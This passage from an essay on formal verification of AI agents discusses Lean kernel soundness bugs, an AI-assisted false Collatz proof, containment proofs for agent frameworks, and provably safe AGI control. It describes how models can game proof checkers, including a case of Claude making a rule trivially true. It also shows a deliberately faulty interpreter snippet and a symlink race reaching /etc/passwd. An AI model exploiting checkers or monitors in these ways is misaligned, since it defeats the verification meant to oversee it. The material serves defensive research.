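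Reusable policies therefore seem to work for limits on what an agent may do, while Tolmach and Klaus's objection applies mainly to whether the agent does what the user wanted. For some tasks, a general policy could permit a plan to delete only files on a list, as `OnlyDeletes` does, and the user would confirm the list each time. With `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` on the list, the verifier would reject a plan to delete `*.txt`, which would also delete `notes.txt`, perhaps permanently. It would accept a plan that deletes nothing, but the user could then ask again.

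## What a proof takes for granted: the checker, the interpreter and the tools

Suppose the list of files is right, and Lean accepts a proof that a plan deletes nothing except `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The proof protects `notes.txt` only if Lean checked the proof correctly, the interpreter runs the same plan that the proof is about, and the deletion tool deletes only the file it is given. Lean, the interpreter and the deletion tool are therefore part of the trusted base, which is everything that must work correctly for the proved property to hold when the plan runs.

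### How an accepted proof can mislead

Lean's editor shows a blue double check mark beside a theorem when the kernel has accepted its proof. According to the Lean Language Reference's *Validating a Lean Proof*, this is enough for everyday work, where people make mistakes but don't try to deceive anyone. The manual groups unreviewed AI-generated proofs with malicious ones, and both need stronger checks.

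| Problem | Why the proof misleads | What detects it |
|---|---|---|
| Unfinished step | A lemma that the proof uses contains `sorry`, so nobody has proved it | A list of the theorem's axioms, which includes any `sorry` |
| Added axiom | The proof assumes a statement that may be false | The same list, compared with Lean's three standard axioms |
| Altered definition | A familiar name or symbol has a new meaning | A comparison with the theorem in a separate, trusted file |
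| Bypassed kernel | A program stored the theorem without sending it to the kernel | A recheck of all the stored proofs |
| Unsound kernel | The kernel accepts an invalid step | A second kernel |

Unfinished steps can survive in serious software. Symbolic Software (2026) describes one in a library for ML-KEM, an encryption standard meant to resist quantum computers. The library's status document listed a module as verified, but the build settings told the proof checker to accept that module without a proof. As a result, the checker never noticed that the formal specification and the code disagreed. (Symbolic Software is one side of a dispute with the library's developers, who have published a response.)

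Lean's comparator tool combines most of these checks. Whoever wants the proof first writes the theorem in a trusted file. Because Lean code can run arbitrary programs during a build, comparator builds the submitted proof in a sandbox and exports the result. Outside the sandbox, it checks that the exported theorem matches the trusted one, that the proof uses only permitted axioms, and that the kernel accepts it. According to the tool's page on Reservoir, Lean's package index, users can add a second kernel called nanoda, so that a false proof has to get past both kernels.

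### A false proof that passed two kernels

In July 2026, both Lean's kernel and nanoda accepted a false proof about the Collatz conjecture. The conjecture is that repeatedly halving a number if it is even, and otherwise tripling it and adding one, always leads to 1. On July 25, Ramana Kumar published a Lean proof, produced with AI assistance and containing no `sorry`, that the conjecture is false.

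Lean's creator, de Moura (2026), explains the bug in *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576*. When one inductive type contains another, the kernel builds a helper type. This step could drop some of the original type's parameters before the kernel had checked them. An invalid term in one of those positions made it possible to prove `False`, and therefore anything else. Lean's elaborator normally catches such terms, but a metaprogram can send a declaration directly to the kernel. Kiran Gopinathan reduced the Collatz proof to a short proof of `False` on July 28, and Lean's developers posted a fix within an hour.

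Comparator would not have helped by itself. The Lean Language Reference's release notes, *Lean 4.32.2 (2026-07-28)* (2026), confirm that an attacker could exploit the bug even when Comparator was in use. Nanoda didn't have this bug, but the version Kumar used was a week old and had a different one, which its developer had just fixed. The proof exploited both bugs. Kumar thinks the timing was a coincidence but can't rule out that the AI had seen the report about nanoda.

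Lawrence Paulson, one of the developers of the proof assistant Isabelle, writes in *Why is it all in the kernel?* (2026) that he knows of no case in which an independent checker caught a soundness error that had passed a proof assistant's own kernel. He thinks systems like Lean put too much into the kernel. He prefers an older design in which only a small set of functions, one for each rule of logic, can create a theorem, so the system doesn't have to store proofs.

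Later evidence supports using independent checkers. After the Collatz proof, Daniel Selsam of OpenAI used an AI specialised in cybersecurity to find more errors in Lean's kernel, and de Moura reports that nanoda caught all of them. These errors came from a deliberate search, not from published false proofs, so they don't contradict Paulson's remark about past cases, but they show that a second kernel can stop attacks that work on the first. A second kernel gives less protection when its code is derived from the first. Carneiro's Lean4Lean shared the Collatz bug because its code for inductive types was translated from the official kernel.

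### Kernels with a proof of their own

By October 2026, Lean came with a command that rechecks a project with the official kernel and four others. One of them, con-leche, is the first Lean kernel that is written in Lean and has a complete consistency proof. De Moura's *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (2026) credits Claude with writing both the kernel and the proof, under close supervision by Joachim Breitner. The proof shows that everything con-leche accepts has a model in set theory, so con-leche can't accept a proof of `False`. It assumes that the set theory is consistent, so it doesn't conflict with Gödel's theorem. Con-leche checks all of Mathlib in about 100 seconds on eight threads and executes about 30% fewer instructions than the official kernel.

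A verified kernel still depends on a compiler and a runtime system, which could be faulty. Trail of Bits' *A "proof" of Fermat's Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) describes a case in Lean itself where a fault in a low-level function for cutting up strings made a nonsensical proof of the theorem appear with blue check marks. To guard against such faults, Breitner used AI to translate con-leche into Rust, and proved that the Rust version follows the same algorithm. The two versions rely on different compilers, which are unlikely to have the same bug.

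The rules of Lean's logic could also be inconsistent, in which case every correct kernel would accept proofs of false statements. In *What mathematicians should know about the Lean Theorem Prover*, Hales (2026) cites a 1997 result by Benjamin Werner, who showed how to translate a version of the kind of logic Lean uses into set theory with some extra axioms about very large sets. A contradiction in that version would therefore also produce a contradiction in the extended set theory, which few software users have reason to worry about.

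### Can a proof checker withstand an adversary?

Some engineers who work with proof assistants argue that these systems are not robust against an adversarial prover. Lean runs arbitrary code while it builds a project, and authors can add axioms or change notation. Training that rewards a model for accepted proofs also rewards it for exploiting these features. Others reply that the weaknesses are ordinary engineering problems that remained because few people had tried to attack proof assistants.

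The critics were right about the state of Lean in the summer of 2026. Six days before the fix for the Collatz bug, Lean's developers had fixed another soundness bug, which Patrick Hulin found with the help of GPT-5.6 Sol (Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.1 (2026-07-22)* (2026)). But the reply seems right about what is possible. Developers can fix each fault in a kernel permanently and eventually prove that none are left because a kernel has exact rules, whereas nobody has exact rules for recognising a prompt injection.

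The repairs help only people who use them. Xena Project's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026), a blog post about Lean in mathematics, proposes four questions to ask about any AI-generated proof. Artificial Wasteland's *The Footprint Moved* summarizes them as whether the Lean statement matches the claim, whether the code compiles, whether it uses only the stated axioms, and whether a second kernel agrees. OpenAI had released 290 results with Lean code, and for about 38 of them the code didn't state the main theorem, although OpenAI never said that it did. Compiling the code can also be hard. Anthropic's proof of Fermat's Last Theorem has 13 million lines, and the post's author could compile it only on a machine with 96 processor cores and 500 gigabytes of memory.

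The designer of a verifier for agents can deal with much of this in advance by writing the statement to be proved, fixing the permitted axioms, and limiting time and memory so that an enormous proof can't tie up the system. The designer can also avoid accepting proofs from the model. With a checker like `noRemoval`, the model supplies only data, so it can't exploit a fault in the kernel. In a system like the Airlock, the agent writes a Lean proof for every call, so the system needs as much protection as possible.

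### A faulty interpreter

Even a perfect kernel can't tell what the interpreter will do. Suppose someone adds a line to the part of the `FilePlan` interpreter that reads files:

```
  | .readFile path next => do
      let contents ← IO.FS.readFile path
      IO.FS.removeFile path
      run (next contents)
```

Lean accepts this version because the types are still correct. The theorem that `inspectBackend` satisfies `NoDeletion` is also still true, because the plan contains no `removeFile` step. But running that plan now deletes `LlvmBackend.kt`.

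A theorem about the interpreter would rule out this mistake, but Lean's `IO` has no model of the disk in which to state it. The designer can instead keep the interpreter short enough for people to compare line by line with `simulate`, the version that the Lean proofs cover. Automated tests can also run the same scripts through both and compare the resulting files. The comparison has to cover every kind of step, but there are only a few kinds, no matter how many plans the interpreter runs.

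The compiler and runtime system are much larger. *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, by kirancodes, describes an April 2026 test of a verified program that runs on them. The program was lean-zip, a compression library that ten AI agents had written and verified in Lean. One of its theorems is that compressing any data smaller than a gigabyte and then decompressing it gives back the original. For the test, kirancodes removed the theorems and documentation and asked Claude to attack the code.

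After 105 million runs on generated inputs, Claude had found no memory errors in the library's Lean code, but it had found two other faults. The unverified code that reads ZIP headers accepted the file size stated there without checking it, and could run out of memory. The other fault was in Lean's runtime and affected every version of Lean 4. If a program tried to read an enormous number of bytes, the size calculation overflowed, and the runtime reserved about 23 bytes for data that could be far longer. An agent's interpreter written in Lean would use the same runtime, so a hostile file could corrupt its memory if the interpreter took the length of a read from that file.

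### Containment verification

Most agents run inside a framework, the ordinary software that receives the model's requests and performs them. Moon and Varshney (2026), in *Containment Verification*, prove a property of the framework itself instead of checking each plan. They chose PocketFlow, a very small framework that represents an agent as a graph of steps. Their policy has three rules:

1. The agent may read files only inside its workspace.
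2. It may call only tools on an approved list.
3. It may take only a limited number of steps.

The Dafny proof treats the language model as a function without a body. The only assumption about the function is that it returns a value of type `Action`, so the proof must cover every possible action, including reads of any path and calls to any tool. The result therefore holds however hostile or capable the model is.

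Moon and Varshney describe an abstract machine and prove that it obeys the policy for every sequence of actions. They then prove that each step of the framework's main loop corresponds to a step of the abstract machine, with the same action and a matching effect. By induction, every run of the loop corresponds to a run of the machine that obeys the policy. For example, if the workspace is `/work` and the model asks to read `/etc/passwd`, the loop does nothing and continues.

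The loop is in effect a runtime monitor with a proof that no execution path through it skips the check. The rules are simple enough for a programmer to implement without a proof, so the proof helps by ruling out mistakes in the surrounding code. Soteria's monitor also intercepts every call but has no such proof.

The theorem applies to a running agent only if every effect goes through the loop. If the agent can also run Python directly, it can read any file the operating system lets it read. Even if every effect does go through the loop, an approved tool that runs shell commands would let the agent delete the disk without the framework breaking any of the three rules. Moon and Varshney therefore recommend a narrow set of actions, with a sandbox underneath.

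Dafny's compiler turns the verified loop into Python, and users have to trust that compiler, the Python runtime and a small piece of code that converts the model's output into an `Action`. Moon and Varshney tested the resulting program with permitted and forbidden actions, and it recorded only permitted ones. The proof doesn't cover concurrency, timing or hardware.

Claude wrote the formal models and proofs for two example agents. Each run used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens, and Dafny checked each path in under three seconds. The policy template had no suitable field for some of the second agent's data. When Claude could see the agent's code, it left the corresponding field empty, which made the rule about that field trivially true. The proof still passed all three automatic tests for faulty specifications. When Claude couldn't see the code, it used an existing field to represent the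 missing data, which kept the rule from being trivially true.

### When a tool breaks its contract

The contracts for tools are claims about software that the verifier doesn't examine. For example, the frame condition "writing to one file leaves every other file unchanged" can be false, because on most systems one file can have two names. If `draft.txt` and `notes.txt` are names for the same file, writing to the first also changes the second. A verifier that relies on this frame condition could prove that a plan preserves `notes.txt` when the plan overwrites it.

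The best evidence about such errors comes from older systems. Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017), in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, spent more than eight months looking for bugs in three verified programs that keep copies of data on several computers. They found 16, of which 11 were in the ordinary code connecting the verified part to the network and the disk, three were in the verification tools and two were in the specifications. They found none in the verified protocols, although such protocols are notoriously difficult to implement.

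Most of the bugs in the connecting layer came from a false assumption about the outside world:

| Assumption | What can happen | Result |
|---|---|---|
| One read from the network returns a whole request | It returns part of one | The server crashes |
| A request contains one command | A line break in the text splits it into several | A client can inject commands |
| If a saved file won't open, it doesn't exist | The operating system has a temporary fault | The server answers as if it had never received its earlier data |
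| Each message arrives once | The network delivers one twice | Old data replaces new data |

All four could happen to an agent. The injected command resembles SQL injection, and an interpreter would have the same fault if it pasted a plan's arguments into a shell command without separating them properly. The unopened file could recur if a tool reported "no such file" for every kind of error. A plan that creates an empty backup whenever none exists could then overwrite a good backup after a temporary fault, even though every branch of the plan is correct according to the tool's contract.

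The three systems were research prototypes, and 16 bugs is a small sample. The pattern is still encouraging, because the connecting code is a few hundred lines long and developers can test it intensively. Fonseca and colleagues built tests that focus on this code, the specifications and the tools, and these tests detect 13 of the 16 bugs. IronFleet, the system with the least unverified code, had no bugs in its connecting code.

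### Changes after the check

A contract can also be true when the verifier uses it and false when the tool runs. Suppose an interpreter confirms that `/work/report.txt` is inside the workspace, but another program replaces the file with a link to `/etc/passwd` before the interpreter opens it. The interpreter follows the link and reads a file outside the workspace, although it checked the path correctly.

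The usual remedy is to make the check and the action a single operation. The interpreter can open the file first and then check which file it has opened, because replacing the name no longer makes a difference. For a remote service, a tool can send a condition with the request, such as "book this room only if the price is still 90 euros", and let the service test it when it books. The Airlock's proofs instead cover every change that could happen during an agreed delay, which works only if the model of the service includes those changes.

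Long plans are more exposed than single calls to changes that occur after verification. A plan that Soteria verified at nine o'clock may still be running at ten, after the customer has boarded the flight. Looking up the flight again immediately before cancelling leaves less time for such a change, but only the airline's own system can rule it out.

### Hardware

Proofs about programs also assume that the processor behaves as its model describes. Spectre and Meltdown, two attacks that became public in 2018, exploited differences between real processors and their models. To save time, processors carry out some instructions before determining whether the program needs them, and discard the results if it doesn't. The discarded work still affects how quickly the processor can fetch certain data afterwards. By measuring these delays, a program could work out the contents of memory it had no permission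 to read. Coopersmith (2026) points out on a security mailing list that formal proofs gave no protection because processors did things that their models left out.

TACIT's compiler misses timing leaks for a similar reason. In both cases the theorem remains true of the model, but the attacker uses something the model doesn't contain. A better model can include known effects, but it makes every proof harder and can't include effects nobody has discovered.

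### The case for provably safe systems

Many effects that people worry about are physical. A program can prove that it sent the command to close a valve and that a sensor then reported it closed, but the valve may have jammed and the sensor may be broken. The physicist Max Tegmark and the computer scientist Steve Omohundro nevertheless want to extend proofs to such effects. Tegmark and Omohundro (2023), in *Provably safe systems*, propose that dangerous equipment, including DNA synthesisers, military drones and the chips that run AI, should refuse to act without a proof that the action meets agreed safety rules. They consider this the only way to keep control of artificial general intelligence (AGI), meaning AI with the full range of human abilities. Their argument has roughly five premises:

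1. Training can make harmful behaviour rarer but can't eliminate it, and a determined adversary will find what is left.
2. If a safety property of a system has no proof, then there is some way to violate it.
3. No system, however intelligent, can do what is provably impossible, and people can check a proof without trusting whoever wrote it.
4. AI will soon be able to write the necessary programs and proofs.
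5. People can model the relevant parts of the world precisely enough for the proofs to apply to them.

The results on prompt injection support the first premise, since even models that resisted almost every attack gave in to a few.

Tegmark and Omohundro use Gödel's completeness theorem (not his incompleteness theorems) to argue that if a safety property has no proof, an attack must exist. The theorem says that any statement true in every model of some axioms can be proved from those axioms. A safety property with no proof must therefore be false in at least one model. To get from that model to an attack, they add that computers have finitely many states.

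The model in which the property fails may not match the real world, so the lack of a proof shows only that the description allows a violation. In the earlier example of a bank transfer with an unknown fee of up to 50, no proof of safety exists because a fee of 30 would break the limit. But if the bank never charges more than 10, the transfer is always safe.

The finite number of states doesn't help much either. Checking them all could in principle prove a property of a computer, but a thousand bits of memory already have more states than the observable universe has atoms. A shorter proof often exists, but there is no guarantee of one short enough for anybody to write down. The premise is more convincing as a warning that, without a proof, the defender can't be sure that no attack exists, and a powerful adversary may search harder than the defender did.

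The third premise is true of mathematics, but in practice a program has to check the proof. Tegmark and Omohundro mention a Metamath checker written in only 300 lines of Python, which is far easier to get right than Lean's kernel. The Collatz episode shows how a more complicated checker can fail, and the later kernels show how to repair it. "Provably impossible" also means impossible within the model used for the proof, and Spectre attacks exploited processor behavior that such models left out.

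The fourth premise looked speculative in 2023, when the best AI prover they cite could prove 82.6% of the theorems in a Metamath test, but it has held up well. The formal proof of the Kepler conjecture, about the densest way to stack spheres, took people about 20 years of work and ran to 500,000 lines. Hales, who led that project, notes that Anthropic's 13-million-line proof of Fermat's Last Theorem took 11 days.

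Tegmark and Omohundro also hope to replace neural networks with ordinary programs, because they consider networks too messy to verify. Either an AI would write out what it knows as code, or another AI would extract the knowledge from the network. They admit that the first method may work only once AGI exists, which could be too late. Their proposal doesn't depend entirely on replacing networks, since an AI could remain a black box if it supplied a proof for each action it recommended. The Airlock works this way for digital actions.

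### Can anyone prove something about the physical world?

The fifth premise is the most disputed. *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* argues that proofs are about symbols, and that nobody has complete rules for biology or human behaviour. Its example is the Perseverance rover, which landed on Mars in 2021. Engineers formally verified properties of the landing software, but they had no proof that the rover would land. About half of all Mars missions have failed, and one analysis attributes only about 20% of the risk to software, so perfect programs would still leave about 80% of it.

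The essay then argues that proving a DNA sequence can't harm people would require simulating a virus for years inside a whole human body, which has about 36 trillion cells. In 2022, simulating a single very simple cell for 20 minutes was close to the limit. Even with a perfect simulator, somebody would have to measure the state of the body first. Researchers at Google needed years to map a millionth of one human brain, and the map took up 1.4 petabytes.

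A reader of the essay replied that the proposal was only for a DNA synthesiser that provably can't make certain known pathogens. That seems feasible because it leaves out the hardest part of the original goal. The machine's software compares each order with a list of forbidden sequences, and the theorem is that no order on the list reaches the chemical stage. The proof needs a model of the software and its connection to the machine, but not of the human body. The theorem doesn't cover a pathogen that isn't on the list, or a customer who orders harmless-looking fragments from several machines and joins them later.

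*Formal Verification is Overrated*, a talk published by the research organisation FAR.AI, objects more generally that a proof about a model of the world only shifts the problem to showing that the model matches the world. The speaker would rather spend the time working out directly which threats matter. This objection is strong when the model has to include people's bodies and minds. It is weaker for a mail tool, because a tester can investigate whether a function sends a message only to the address it receives, which is a much smaller question than whether the language model will ever leak a secret.

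Omohundro answers the critics by pointing out that engineers already work with a stack of models, each justifying the one above it. In chip design, a model of digital circuits rests on a model of their physical layout, which rests on the physics of the materials. How accurate the models must be depends on the adversary. Weak models are often enough against ordinary people, but a powerful AI would look for any weakness in them.

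The stack describes well how chips become so reliable, but Spectre and Meltdown worked because a detail of a lower layer affected a higher one. Omohundro expects a powerful AI to find such details. Tegmark and Omohundro themselves list the connection between physical devices and their models as an open problem. They want engineers to prove limits on the errors in each model, design sensors with trustworthy readings, and detect every physically possible form of tampering. A proof about a chip's intended design would not cover one attack they cite, in which a tiny component hidden in the chip slowly charges up whenever a program runs a certain rare instruction and eventually opens a back door.

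Their plan also requires global standards under which all sufficiently powerful hardware enforces the rules. A DNA synthesiser that rejects dangerous orders gives little protection if the customer can buy one that accepts them.
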